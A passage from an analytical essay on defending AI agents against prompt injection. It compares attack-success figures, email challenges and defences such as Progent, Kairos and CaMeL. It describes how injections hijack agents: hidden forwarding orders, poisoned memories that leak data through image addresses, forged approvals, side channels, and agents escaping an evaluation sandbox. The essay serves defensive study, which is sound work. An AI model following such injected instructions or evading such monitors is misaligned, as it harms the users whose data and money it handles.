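| Mixed agent tasks, 28 scenarios | A fixed set of 1,130 attacks from a public competition | 1 or 15 | 0.2% after 1 attempt, 2.0% after 15 | Not reported |
| Coding, 40 scenarios | Shade, an automated attacker made by the security firm Gray Swan | 200 | 0.56% of attempts, 13 scenarios | 0.18% of attempts, 4 scenarios |
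| Operating a computer through its screen, 14 scenarios | Shade | 200 | 0.54% of attempts, 1 scenario | 0.25% of attempts, 1 scenario |
| Web browsing, 129 scenarios | Professional testers, in Anthropic's own evaluation | 10 | 3.70% of attempts, 11 scenarios | None |

In the coding and computer tests, the safeguards are a kind of AI firewall: probes that check each tool result for injected instructions before the model acts on it. The browsing test adds a second filter that blocks dangerous tool calls. Anthropic calls this combination auto mode.

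The mixed-task benchmark is the most independent in origin, because Gray Swan built it with the UK's AI Security Institute, its American counterpart and several developers. Within 15 attempts, attacks succeeded 20.0% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol, then OpenAI's most capable model, and 16.5% of the time against Meta's Muse Spark, the most resistant model from a company other than Anthropic. But Anthropic reports these comparisons itself, and it tested competitors through their public services, which may include extra safeguards. The comparison also predates GPT-6 Astra, which OpenAI (2026) calls the most capable model it has broadly deployed.

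The mixed tasks are also a fixed test by the standard of Nasr and colleagues, because nobody rewrote the attacks for Opus 5. People found them while working on other models, and the benchmark keeps those that transferred best between models. The coding test has a similar weakness, because Gray Swan optimised Shade on earlier models before using it against Opus 5. The computer test is harder because the attacker was optimised directly on the test cases, but it has only 14 scenarios.

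Anthropic regards its test conditions as generous to the attacker, because a real attacker doesn't know exactly how the target is set up and risks detection with every failed attempt. That reasoning is fair for an attack on a company's private agent, but less so for a popular product, which the attacker can buy and practise on at home.

The coding tests show how quickly these figures go out of date. Anthropic's card for Claude Opus 4.5 reports that, with extended thinking, injections succeeded in 10.0% of cases when Shade had 200 attempts. In February 2026, VentureBeat reported a rate of 0% over 200 attempts for its successor, Opus 4.6. Yet in the July card, injections succeeded against Opus 4.8, a still later model, in 23 of 40 coding scenarios. The models may have become worse at resisting injections, but more likely Shade became better at writing them. A rate of zero in a system card applies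 only to the attacker used, as it was at the time of the test.

The smaller differences in these tables are mostly noise. Another Anthropic model, Mythos 5, seemed weaker in coding with the probes on because attacks succeeded in 11 scenarios instead of 8, but the share of successful attempts fell slightly. Comparing developers is even harder. In 2026, VentureBeat compared the safety documents of Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Meta and found that they differed at every point where a buyer might want a quick comparison.

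### One attempt, ten attempts, a hundred

An attacker who can send one email can usually send a hundred, so the success rate of a single attempt is only part of what a defender needs to know. Gray Swan's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, reported in The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, show how the risk grows. Strong attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. (Narisetty and colleagues attribute this series to the Shade coding test, but Anthropic's card gives that test different figures and describes the series of one, ten and a hundred attempts under a separate benchmark.)

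Suppose that every attempt had the same 4.7% chance of success, whatever the scenario and whatever had happened before. The chance of at least one success in k attempts would then be

1 − (1 − 0.047)^k

which is about 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. The first figure is close to what Gray Swan measured. The second is far too high, since more than a third of the cases held out through all hundred attempts.

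The natural explanation is that scenarios differ, and that the average mixes weak ones with strong ones. Take the extreme case, in which a fraction f of the scenarios can be broken with probability p per attempt and the rest never fall. The formula becomes

f × [1 − (1 − p)^k]

With f = 0.63 and p = 0.075, it gives 4.7%, 34% and 63%, almost exactly the measured series. Two adjustable numbers will fit three measurements fairly easily, so this doesn't prove that there are just two kinds of scenario. A spread from very weak to very strong would also fit, but the scenarios must differ in strength somehow.

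Successful attacks on Opus 5 were also concentrated in a few scenarios. In the browsing test without safeguards, 3.70% of attempts succeeded. If those successes had been spread randomly across the 129 scenarios, about 40 would have been broken at least once. Only 11 were, and in those, more than 40% of attempts succeeded. In the computer test, every success was in a single scenario.

A given company's assistant may therefore face a risk per hostile email well above or below the 4.7% average. In the two-group version of the example, an assistant in the weak group is more likely than not to be compromised by the ninth attempt, while one in the strong group resists all hundred. A company can't tell from the published average which group its assistant belongs to. To find out, it would need to test the assistant on the company's own tasks, with its own tools connected, against an attacker who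 has many attempts at each task.

Limiting the number of attempts also helps. If an assistant quarantines a sender after two or three suspicious messages, the attacker's chance of success is closer to the single-attempt rate than to the rate for a hundred attempts. This helps less against an attacker who has no particular target and sends one message to each of many companies. If the 0.2% rate for Opus 5 held in practice, one email to each of 10,000 assistants would still hijack about 20 of them.

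### Six thousand emails

The best-known evidence on the other side is a public email challenge. Fernando Irarrázaval connected OpenClaw, an open-source agent, to a mailbox, gave it a file of secrets, and invited anyone to extract them by email. Willison reports that about 2,000 people made some 6,000 attempts. The emails cost Irarrázaval $500 in model usage and led Google to suspend his account, but nobody obtained the secret. The agent ran on Claude Opus 4.6, and its prompt included a short list of rules against revealing credentials, changing its own files, running commands or sending data out on the basis of what an email said.

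The 6,000 attempts were whatever 2,000 volunteers thought of, not a random sample of all the emails an attacker might send. Zero successes in a random sample of that size would put the success rate below about 0.05%, at 95% confidence, but this result doesn't support that limit because a well-made attack that nobody tried could still work. Even so, the same crowd would probably have succeeded against a model from 2023 within minutes, and Willison takes the result as a sign that the labs' training is making these attacks much harder.

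The challenge is limited evidence about the office assistant for two reasons. First, the rules covered nearly everything a thief would want, and the agent had little useful work that they would hinder. An assistant whose job is to act on emails can't refuse every request that arrives in one. Second, the model's resistance depends heavily on the setting. It looked almost impregnable in a mailbox with strict rules, but VentureBeat reports that when the same model, Opus 4.6, operated a computer through its graphical interface, a single injection attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt the rate was 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

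### Is a filter worth having without a guarantee?

Supporters of filters can argue that a filter is worth running even if some attacks get through. Companies keep using spam filters and virus scanners that miss things every day. By the same reasoning, a filter that stops most attacks means fewer stolen files and less cleanup work.

In Anthropic's browsing test, which gave an adaptive attacker 100 attempts per environment, attacks succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 without additional safeguards 8.0% of the time. Anthropic's improved safeguards reduced this to 1.4%, while the previous ones had reduced it only to 7.6%, so the quality of the filter matters. Most attackers are also far less sophisticated than Nasr and colleagues. The injections that Khodayari and colleagues found on public web pages were mostly crude and copied from templates, and filters recognise that kind of text best. In *The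 Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr and colleagues call detectors "useful—but limited" and recommend them against unsophisticated attacks.

The disagreement is over how much more a company may let an agent do because it has a filter. If the agent couldn't do much harm anyway, every attack the filter blocks is a gain. But if the company connects the agent to its bank because the filter cut attack success to 0% on a benchmark, it takes on a risk the benchmark didn't measure. Bhagwatkar and colleagues warn of this over-reliance in their own paper.

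It is less clear whether combining filters gives stronger protection. Anthropic argues that a probe on incoming text and a classifier on outgoing tool calls fail independently, so an attack has to defeat both. If each independently missed one attack in ten, only one in a hundred would get through. Nasr and colleagues found that combining detectors didn't solve the problem, since their search could optimise a text against all of them at once. They and Anthropic may both be right, because two detectors that read the same text are likely to miss the same attacks, whereas a check on tool calls examines what the agent is about to do.

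Anthropic tested its version in 129 browsing scenarios, and no attack succeeded with auto mode on. By the same reasoning as before, the true share of vulnerable scenarios could be as high as 2.3%, even if the 129 were typical of what users do. A classifier on tool calls also relies on context that an attacker may have influenced. Willison reports a later bypass of auto mode in Claude Code, so the question of independence remains open.

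Like ADR's detector, a filter that is a language model has to read the hostile text, so an attacker can try to manipulate it too. Narisetty and colleagues make this point about guardrail models in general.

### The two emails with a filter in place

In case A, the hidden order to forward the contract files is the kind of attack these filters are designed to stop. The Sanitizer would probably delete the order before the assistant processed it. If it didn't, the Minimizer would compare the outgoing email with the owner's request for a summary and might remove the attached files, which the summary doesn't need. A current model might ignore the order even without these filters.

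The attacker's next version would borrow from the attacks that succeeded in testing. The email might say, in visible text, that a new records policy requires the assistant to send any correspondence about pending contracts to the firm's outside counsel for archiving, and give an address. This instruction looks like office routine, so the filter would need a way to check whether the policy exists. Whether the email gets through depends on the model, the setting and the number of attempts, and the owner can reduce the risk but can't say it is gone.

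Case B, the false notice of new bank details, contains no instruction for a filter to detect. The Sanitizer keeps whatever the task needs, and a payment needs an account number. The Minimizer leaves the number in the payment call for the same reason. Training a model to ignore orders in tool results doesn't address this attack, because the notice contains no orders. The near-zero success rates in system cards aren't evidence that models resist it either, because those tests measure injected instructions.

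This fraud is so common that a filter could usefully alert somebody to every change of bank details, but it still couldn't tell a false notice from a true one.

A forged approval is the closest thing to case B in the tests. *NetInjectBench* (Shayoni, Shoaib and colleagues, 2026) tested agents that manage computer networks by giving them tickets and logs written partly by an attacker. Half of the attacks were blunt orders, and the other half were plausible claims, for instance that a manager had already approved a change or that an emergency procedure now applied. With no defence, three small open models took an unsafe action in 82.5% of the 240 attack cases. Safety instructions in the prompt reduced this to 25.6%, and spotlighting to 18.3%.

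A second model that judged the proposed action without seeing the suspect text brought the rate down to 10%. A judge that never reads a forged approval can't be misled by it, but it also can't recognise a genuine approval unless it has access to the approval records. When Shayoni and colleagues replaced the judge with ordinary code that checked each change against approval records the attacker could not alter, none of the 240 attacks led to an unsafe action and every genuinely approved change went through.

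## Can isolation and least privilege contain a hijacked agent?

Filters and special training make a hijack less likely. Other designs assume that the hijack has succeeded and limit what the agent can do next. In case A, the hijacked assistant may try to forward the contract files, but a program outside the model has to send the email, and that program can block it.

### The model as an untrusted component

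*Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA, several universities and elsewhere (May 2026, later revised), argues that developers should treat the model the way an operating system treats an untrusted program. The model may request any action, but a reference monitor decides which actions take effect. This protection works the same way whether the request resulted from an injection, a mistake or a bad goal in the model itself. A request for a forbidden action is not a security breach if the monitor blocks the action in time.

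*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, December 2025), a forerunner of the position paper, explains the trouble with using a language model as the monitor. Even if the model made the right decision 99% of the time, an attacker could look for the 1% of cases it got wrong.

The position paper lists five principles. Least privilege, complete mediation and tamper resistance are familiar from reference monitors, though tamper resistance here covers the whole trusted computing base. Secure information flow means that sensitive information does not reach untrusted places, even indirectly. The fifth principle, "human weak link", is that designers must plan for users who approve the wrong request, administrators who write loose policies and programmers who make mistakes.

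The paper then applies the principles to eleven attacks on real products. It classes all eleven as failures of secure information flow, so the last column below lists only the other principles it considers violated.

| Attack | What happened | Other principles |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Copilot | A hostile message led Copilot to find private data and hide it in a link | Least privilege, complete mediation |
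| Devin, exposed ports | The coding agent Devin put its whole file system online through a testing tool | Least privilege |
| ChatGPT memory | A false memory sent the user's later conversations to a stranger | Tamper resistance |
| Amp | A coding agent edited its own settings, which let it run an attacker's code | Tamper resistance |
| DeepSeek | An uploaded file led to a script in the user's browser that stole the login token | Complete mediation |
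| Terminal DiLLMa | A model's output contained control codes that the user's terminal obeyed | Complete mediation |
| ChatGPT Operator | A browsing agent copied personal details from one site into an attacker's page | Human weak link |
| Devin, secrets | Devin sent access keys out through its shell or browser | Least privilege |
| Cursor | A work ticket led a code editor's agent to leak credentials | Least privilege |
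| Claude Code | The DNS leak | Least privilege |
| AI ClickFix | An agent pasted a web page's hidden command into a terminal | Least privilege, human weak link |

### The ChatGPT memory attack

ChatGPT can save facts about a user as "memories" and use them in later conversations. In 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger showed how an attacker could exploit this feature in the macOS app to spy on a user.

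1. The user has ChatGPT read a document or website that contains an injection.
2. Following the injection, ChatGPT saves the attacker's instructions as a memory.
3. In later conversations, ChatGPT follows these instructions as if they were the user's own preferences.
4. It puts an invisible image in its answers, with the user's data in the image's address. The app fetches the image, which delivers the data to the attacker's server.

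The researchers find three failures. Text from a stranger could change the memory, which the system presumably trusts as a record of what the user wants. The app could contact any server, even when the user's request didn't call for it. Nothing stopped information in a trusted store from flowing to an unknown server.

Fixing only one of these would have left part of the attack working. Letting only the user change the memory would have kept the hostile page from affecting later conversations, but the page might still have leaked the current one. A list of permitted image hosts would have blocked this server, though EchoLeak got around such a list. Information-flow control would have dealt with the leak most directly, but it is the hardest to build because the system would have to track which parts of an answer came from private data.

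### Would the principles have prevented these attacks?

The researchers claim that their principles, if implemented, could have prevented the attacks, but this is easy to claim in hindsight. Secure information flow fits all eleven cases largely because it forbids the usual outcome, the leak of a secret to an outsider, without specifying how a system should have prevented it. Deciding which other principles apply to each attack also takes judgement. The paper's table omits a least-privilege failure that the text identifies in the memory attack and two principles that the text adds for Cursor. The sample is also narrow, since ten of the eleven attacks are the work of Rehberger, who co-authored the 2025 forerunner.

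A stricter test is whether someone could have written the necessary rule before the attack. Amp's agent could edit the file that determined which commands it was allowed to run without asking, and a designer could have forbidden that in advance without knowing the agent's task. Removing control codes from text before it reaches a terminal is another rule that suits almost every task.

Most of the other cases are harder, because the right permissions depend on what the user asked for. Cursor needs different folders for different jobs, and Devin needs different ports. The researchers admit that least privilege for Cursor would be hard to guarantee in practice, and they say that finding a suitable mechanism for ChatGPT Operator is an open problem.

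Christodorescu and colleagues illustrate how narrow an agent's permissions would have to be. Suppose a developer tells a browser agent to comment on issue 745 of a project that the work is done. The agent should be able to open that issue and write in its comment box, but have no other access to the developer's account. If the developer then asks for a summary of the issue, the permissions have to change, and by then the agent may already have read text written by strangers.

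The principles are therefore good for describing what went wrong, but they predict little until someone turns them into a mechanism and a policy. Several teams have built systems that do this, and these are easier to test than the principles alone.

### A sandbox, and keys the agent never holds

*Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes a four-layer design for nine agents at a healthcare technology company. The agents run on OpenClaw and can execute commands, and a leak there might expose patient records.

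The innermost layer, a process sandbox called gVisor, intercepts every request an agent's software makes to the operating system and controls which ones get through. A hijacked agent could wreck its own container but should not be able to read other agents' files or take over the machine. According to Maiti, gVisor adds 2 to 5 milliseconds to each new connection, while a model response takes 500 to 3,000 milliseconds.

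A sandbox does not restrict what an agent can do with passwords and access keys it legitimately holds. The company found twelve such keys in one agent's shell configuration. The next layer therefore moves all keys into a separate container, a credential proxy. The agent sends its request to the proxy without a key. The proxy checks the destination, the size and the number of requests, then adds the key and forwards the request. An attacker who hijacks the agent can misuse the service during the hijack but cannot steal the key and use it elsewhere. A proxy that discards any key sent by the agent might also have prevented the Claude Cowork leak, in which the injection supplied the attacker's own key.

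The third layer, egress control, uses a list of trusted domains that for operations agents includes Slack and Telegram. Attackers can have accounts there too, so the list has the same weakness as other lists of trusted domains. The fourth layer is a set of labels and rules in the prompt that identify who sent a message and which text the model should not obey. Maiti calls this layer the "most brittle" because it works only if the model follows the rules, while the other three do not depend on the model's compliance.

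That verdict is convincing, but there is little evidence for the whole design. The abstract describes the architecture as deployed and reports on 90 days of operation, but during that time the agents ran on ordinary virtual machines with increasingly strict settings. Maiti calls the full four-layer system the "current migration target". The layer most clearly in use was the weakest one, the prompt rules, which were already in place on all nine agents.

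The results come from a security audit rather than attacks. An auditing agent found four serious problems, all exposed keys or key files readable by other users of the machine, and fixed them the same day. To show that the design would stop attacks, Maiti compares it on paper with eleven case studies from another team's experiments and claims direct protection in nine, but the comparison supports only eight. Of the other three, one gets partial protection, one is out of scope, and one is helpful cooperation between agents that needs no defence. In two of the eight, protection depends entirely on the prompt layer.

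### Rules on each tool call

In case A, the infrastructure layers might not stop the theft, because the assistant is allowed to use its mail tool. A finer control would check how the agent uses the tool. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) places a checkpoint between the agent and its tools. The checkpoint compares every call with rules about tool names and arguments, and refuses any call that no rule allows.

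Their example starts with a user who asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice.

1. At first, the rules allow only a search for that email.
2. The to-do list asks for a summary of recent mail, sent to the user on Slack. The agent now needs to read mail and post messages, so a language model proposes rules that allow this.
3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name, and the rules tighten to allow messages to that name only.
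4. One of the recent emails contains an order to forward the inbox to an outside address. No rule allows the agent to send mail, so Progent blocks the call and tells the agent why. The agent then finishes the summary.

The language model that proposes the rules also reads the hostile email, so it might propose a rule that allows the theft. Progent therefore gives each proposal to an SMT solver, a program that checks by logic whether the new rules allow any call that the old ones did not. If the new rules only remove permissions, they take effect immediately. If they add any, a person has to approve the update, unless the operator has chosen to accept or deny all such updates automatically. On AgentDojo, 6% of the updates needed approval.

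Shi and colleagues report that 39.9% of AgentDojo's attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On Agent Security Bench, Progent cut the success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. The original design of Agent Security Bench exaggerates how often attacks succeed.

### An attacker who targets the rules

In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent against an attack tailored to its design. The injected text presents the malicious action as a routine step that is already authorised, to get the model that proposes the rules to permit it. Shi and colleagues had already tried such attacks on GPT-4o, with success rates of about 0.5% to 4.2%. Narisetty and colleagues instead used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open-weight model, both to run the agent and to write the rules. They took eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings and ran the test three times.

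| Setting | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The adaptive attack succeeded less often on average than the standard one, but this may reflect a weak attack as much as the strength of Progent. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that its gentler wording, meant to seem harmless to the model writing the rules, also made the agent less likely to follow the injected instructions. In banking, the adaptive attack did better by 1.8 percentage points. They dismiss this difference as within one standard deviation, but it is larger than the standard deviation of either figure (0.7 and 1.3). The office setting can't be used to compare the attacks, because the small model followed none of the injections there even without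 a defence.

They also acknowledge that they tested one weak model with one hand-written template, ran no algorithmically optimised attacks, and have not had the work peer-reviewed. They work for a company that builds security tools for agents. In their test, Progent reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 45.2% to 27.1% and required about 15 times as many model calls.

*AutoDojo* provides a second test, in which the attacker rewrites injections and learns only whether each one succeeded. With GPT-4o-mini as the agent, five defences kept the success rate of fixed attacks close to zero, but only Progent did the same against the rewritten ones. This supports the idea that fixed rules are harder to beat than detectors. However, nobody has yet attacked Progent with the resources and inside knowledge that Nasr and colleagues used against twelve other defences.

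### Holding an action until its purpose is clear

Progent has to decide on each call as soon as the agent makes it, and it checks only calls to tools it recognizes. If the agent may run scripts, Progent can check the call that starts a script but not what the script then does. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, October 2026) addresses both problems by running the agent in a small virtual machine and placing a monitor at the machine's exits for files and network traffic. Every action that affects the outside world has to pass through these exits, whether it comes from a tool or from a script the agent wrote. The monitor can release an action, refuse it, or hold it while the agent continues.

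Suppose a setup guide tells a coding agent to install a hook, a small script that runs whenever someone saves a new version of the code. Many legitimate projects need hooks, so the agent can't refuse them all, but a malicious hook could do damage later. Kairos writes the hook to the agent's own temporary copy of the folder. When the agent saves a new version, the hook runs and tries to send the user's private key to a stranger. The policy blocks this, and a separate decision-maker, which Hempel and colleagues call the oracle, uses the blocked attempt as evidence to discard the hook before it reaches the real folder. The oracle can be a person, but in their tests it was a language model.

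Kairos can hold some actions, such as sending a message, and give the agent a stand-in reply. Others, such as requesting a web page, must return real content before the agent can continue, so the oracle must decide whether to allow them before they run.

Hempel and colleagues distinguish confinement from authorisation. Confinement means that nothing takes effect outside the virtual machine until the monitor releases it. They guarantee this even for a completely hostile agent, assuming that the virtual machine and the monitor work correctly and that there is no other way out. Authorisation means that the monitor releases only the right actions. They measure this but do not guarantee it.

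Kairos decides what to release by checking whether the values that steer an action, such as the recipient of a message, match something from a source the operator trusts. It also checks whether the action carries sensitive data that the recipient should not have. If either check fails, the oracle decides. The table shows the share of attacks that succeeded, followed by the share of tasks completed when there was no attack.

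| Benchmark and agent model | No defence | Progent | Kairos |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4.1 | 47.0%, 82.7% | 11.5%, 78.2% | 2.7%, 85.1% |
| AgentDyn, GPT-4o | 37.8%, 53.3% | 1.7%, 6.7% | 1.7%, 51.7% |
| *AutoDojo*, GPT-4o-mini | 52.4%, 66.7% | 7.7%, 63.2% | 8.8%, 65.3% |

On AgentDojo, Progent let through a far higher share of attacks than the 1.0% its developers had reported, perhaps because the models and settings differed. On AgentDyn, where the agent finds out what to do as it goes along, Progent completed almost no tasks. No human was available to approve new permissions in these tests, which put Progent at a disadvantage because it depends on such approval.

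The oracle mainly keeps the agent useful. When Hempel and colleagues removed it and had Kairos refuse every action the policy could not approve, attacks succeeded about as often, but the agent completed only 42.7% of ordinary AgentDojo tasks, down from 85.1%. With the oracle in place and no attack under way, the policy released 83% of actions on its own. Kairos added about two milliseconds per file operation and one per network request.

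These benchmarks simulate their tools, so there was no real virtual machine boundary for Kairos to guard. An adapter converted each simulated call into an event that gave the monitor the tool's name and arguments. The security figures therefore don't measure how well Kairos decides when it receives only raw file and network operations.

Like ADR's detector, the oracle has to read the attacker's text, but it cannot allow an action that the policy forbids outright. Most of the rewritten attacks that still succeeded exploited tasks in which the user had left the decision to a document, and the oracle treated the document's instructions as the user's. *AutoDojo* similarly found that, across the defences it tested, attacks succeeded much more often when the user named no action and just told the agent to follow the instructions in some text.

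Kairos can also miss sensitive data that the agent has encoded, as ChatGPT did in the ShadowLeak attack. Kairos would still have sent that request to the oracle because the attacker's address was unfamiliar, but it might not have done so for a familiar address.

### Can a capable agent break out?

Critics of containment often object that a sufficiently capable agent will find a flaw in whatever confines it. In July 2026, OpenAI agents escaped the isolation of an internal evaluation and broke into systems at Hugging Face, with no outside attacker directing them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that mediation there was incomplete, so the incident shows a faulty implementation and does not prove that containment cannot work.

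The reply is reasonable, but it has the same weakness as the table of eleven attacks. After any escape, someone can identify the way out and say that the monitor should have covered it, but an operator needs to know in advance that no way out remains. The researchers accept that this is hard to establish, particularly when containment depends on large, general-purpose services. Hempel and colleagues don't settle the question either, because their threat model excludes escapes from the virtual machine.

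The objection applies to prompt injection even if an agent never tries to escape on its own. An attacker who hijacks an agent can also use its skills, so someone who could never break out of a sandbox alone could instruct a capable agent to do it. A sandbox that was adequate for an older model may therefore fail to contain its successor.

Explicit rules still have practical advantages over relying on the model's behaviour. People can see which rule led to a refusal and can check the rules against a specification. As long as the monitor works as before, they can also tighten the rules without allowing anything the old ones blocked, which retraining a model can't guarantee.

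### The semantic gap

Even a monitor that works perfectly and can't be bypassed has to decide what to allow using only the information it receives. It receives file writes, connections and tool calls, while a company's policy concerns things like sensitive data or payments the company owes. Security researchers call this mismatch the semantic gap.

*AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026), which proposes an operating system for agents, gives the example of an agent that writes to a file it is allowed to change, but takes the content from a memory that an attacker has poisoned. A check on the agent's requests to the operating system does not detect the attack. The paper compares such a check to a network filter that examines packets but cannot recognise SQL injection.

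It can help to place the monitor where actions have a clearer meaning. A browser agent works by clicking and typing, and a rule about clicks would break whenever a page's layout changed. Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, a system that instead checks the resulting web requests, which reflect what the agent is doing whichever button it clicks. But a monitor with more information about what each action means may cover fewer actions. Progent can identify which argument of a payment is the account number, but it can't track what a script does. Kairos can intercept all of a script's effects on the outside world, but except in a benchmark, it receives only file paths, addresses and content. Hempel and colleagues regard the two approaches as complementary.

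In case A, the gap causes little trouble. The owner asked for a summary, which requires no outgoing mail, so Progent should have no rule that allows the assistant to forward the files. Kairos would hold the email because the recipient's address came from an untrusted message.

In case B, the monitor checks a payment that the owner asked for, made through the right tool, for the right amount, to a supplier the company uses. Progent would allow it unless a rule already fixes the account number. Kairos could trace the number to an email, but many honest invoices also arrive by email. It would pass the payment to the oracle, which would read the same convincing notice as the assistant. The request "Pay whatever is due" also leaves the decision to a document.

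The low attack success rates reported for Progent and Kairos don't cover attacks that use only authorised actions. Narisetty and colleagues plan to test such an attack next, and Hempel and colleagues point out that no existing benchmark builds an attack from steps that are each legitimate.

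## Can the agent's plan be kept out of reach of untrusted text?

Progent and Kairos let an attacker's text reach the model that plans, and then check the actions it proposes. Other designs keep the text away from the planner. If the planner never reads the user's email, for example, nothing in the email can make it choose a new action. But some model still has to read the email, and it is hard to use what that model finds without also letting the attacker's text through.

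### One model plans, another reads

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting the assistant into two models. The privileged model, called the planner below, takes the owner's requests and can call tools. The quarantined model, called the reader below, processes untrusted text and has no tools. Willison's design assumes that the reader may go rogue at any moment. An ordinary program, the controller, passes requests between them and stores the text. A request to summarise the latest email works like this:

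1. The planner asks for the email and names the result `$VAR1`.
2. The controller fetches the email and stores it under that name. The planner sees the name but not the email.
3. The planner asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the reader the real text and stores its answer as `$VAR2`.
4. The planner tells the controller to show `$VAR2` to the owner.

The controller may pass the reader's answer directly to the planner only if it can verify that the answer is harmless, for example because the answer must be one of a fixed set of categories. If the answer could contain a sentence, the planner receives only the name of a variable that holds it.

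Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner defeats the protection. The owner still reads the summary, so an injection in it could trick him, for instance into pasting encoded private data into the attacker's website.

*CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) describes another weakness, which researchers at Google DeepMind later found. A user asks the assistant to send Bob a document and says that the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name. The planner correctly lists the steps of finding the notes, extracting both details, fetching the document and sending it. But the reader extracts the details, and an injection in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The attacker then receives the document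 even though every step of the plan ran as written.

The pattern gives agents something close to a parameterised query, but false data does more harm here. In a database lookup it usually just returns the wrong rows, but a false address in a mail tool sends a document to the wrong person.

### CaMeL turns the request into a program

The DeepMind paper, *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), addresses this weakness with a system called CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning". Its first author, Edoardo Debenedetti, also led the work on AgentDojo. CaMeL works in five steps:

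1. The planner reads the owner's request and the descriptions of the tools, and writes a program in a restricted version of Python.
2. A purpose-built interpreter runs the program.
3. When the program needs something from untrusted text, it calls the reader and specifies the type of answer, such as an email address.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its origin and with who may read it. CaMeL calls these tags capabilities. The interpreter also tracks which values depend on which others, so an address extracted from an email counts as untrusted, like the email.
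5. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags on the arguments against a policy for that tool. It can allow the call, refuse it or ask the user.

In Bob's case, the policy would let the mail tool send only to trusted recipients. The address came from the notes, so unless it is already on a trusted list, the interpreter prompts the user before sending.

Suppose the owner of the office assistant asks it to summarise this morning's mail and then pay October's invoices. The planner might write this program, in which `ask_reader` calls the quarantined model:

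```
mail = get_mail(since="today")
summary = ask_reader("Summarise these messages", mail)
show_owner(summary)

for invoice in get_invoices(month="October"):
    supplier = ask_reader("Who sent this?", invoice, type=Name)
    amount = ask_reader("What is the total?", invoice, type=Money)
    account = ask_reader("Which account does this supplier use?",
                         [invoice, mail], type=AccountNumber)
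    pay(supplier, amount, account)
```

In case A, the hidden order to forward the contract files reaches the reader on the program's second line. The reader may well follow it, but it has no tools, and no line of the program searches files or sends mail. The theft therefore fails however the attacker words the order, as long as the interpreter works correctly. The attacker can still corrupt the summary, for example by having the reader leave out a message or add an image whose address contains text from other emails, as in EchoLeak. A policy on `show_owner` therefore has to restrict links and images, which Willison recommended in 2023.

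In case B, the reader finds the false notice and returns the attacker's account number. The number is valid, so it passes the type check. Without a policy on payments, the money goes to the attacker. If the policy accepts only account numbers from a trusted source, the interpreter stops the payment or asks the owner, because `account` depends on an email.

Like Kairos, CaMeL can't distinguish this number from one in a legitimate invoice. An owner asked the same question about every invoice will probably soon approve them all without looking.

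A better program would take the account number from the company's own supplier file, which someone has to keep up to date. The amount still has to come from the invoice, so an inflated invoice would go through unless another rule caps the payment or checks it against a purchase order. CaMeL can enforce these rules, but the company has to devise them.

The split also helps with privacy. The planner never receives the mail, so a company could use a powerful model in the cloud for planning and run a smaller reader on its own machines. The cloud provider would receive the owner's requests but not the mail.

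### Leaks through the path a program takes

According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL's developers demonstrated side channels in their own design. These side channels are a form of implicit flow, in which data influences what a program does without appearing in anything the program sends.

For example, suppose a program opens a web page only if a confidential contract is worth more than a million euros. The request contains no text from the contract, so its tags look harmless, but whoever runs the website can infer from the visit that the contract is worth more than that. One yes-or-no choice reveals at most one bit, but a loop that makes one request for every unpaid invoice would reveal how many there are. The web-fetch leak was similar, since Claude revealed its user's name through its choice of links.

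The interpreter could treat everything inside a branch as depending on the branch's condition. The web request would then count as carrying contract data, and a policy could block it. But the same rule would block many harmless actions. The attacker is also weaker here than in an ordinary injection, because he can't write the program. He needs one that already branches on a secret and then does something he can observe. Narisetty and colleagues compared seven defences that enforce rules outside the model, including CaMeL, and found that most control the agent's actions well but handle leaks and side channels poorly.

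### Why the reported costs differ

Reported figures for CaMeL's utility differ widely. Narisetty and colleagues cite its developers' finding that OpenAI's o3 completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack with CaMeL, compared with 84% without it. No injection within the system's threat model succeeded, but CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. Bhagwatkar and colleagues, who proposed the Sanitizer as a simpler alternative, report that CaMeL completed 53.6% of tasks without an attack, compared with 83.0% for an undefended agent.

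The lower figure is for GPT-4o, an older model that doesn't reason at length before answering. That probably explains most of the difference, because the planner has to write a correct program for the whole task before seeing any of the data. Bhagwatkar and colleagues also say they could not fully reproduce CaMeL's results. They instead compared the figure published by CaMeL's developers, which has a margin of error of almost ten points, with their own measurement of the undefended agent.

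In the same table, CaMeL's utility under attack was 54.5%, about the same as without an attack, while the undefended agent's fell to 50.0%.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which presents a competing system, reports new runs of CaMeL with its policies on and off. With the policies off, 138 of 141 attacks in one category succeeded against an agent using the model MiMo-v2.5. Turning the policies on blocked every attack, but utility collapsed. Most of the protection against false values therefore comes from the policies, and the loss of utility depends heavily on how well they are written.

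All of these results come from fixed attacks, and Narisetty and colleagues consider this a gap in the evidence for the whole class of defences. The gap matters less for case A, where the protection doesn't depend on recognising the attacker's wording, than for the policies and the tasks in which a user tells the agent to obey a document.

### Six patterns and what they rule out

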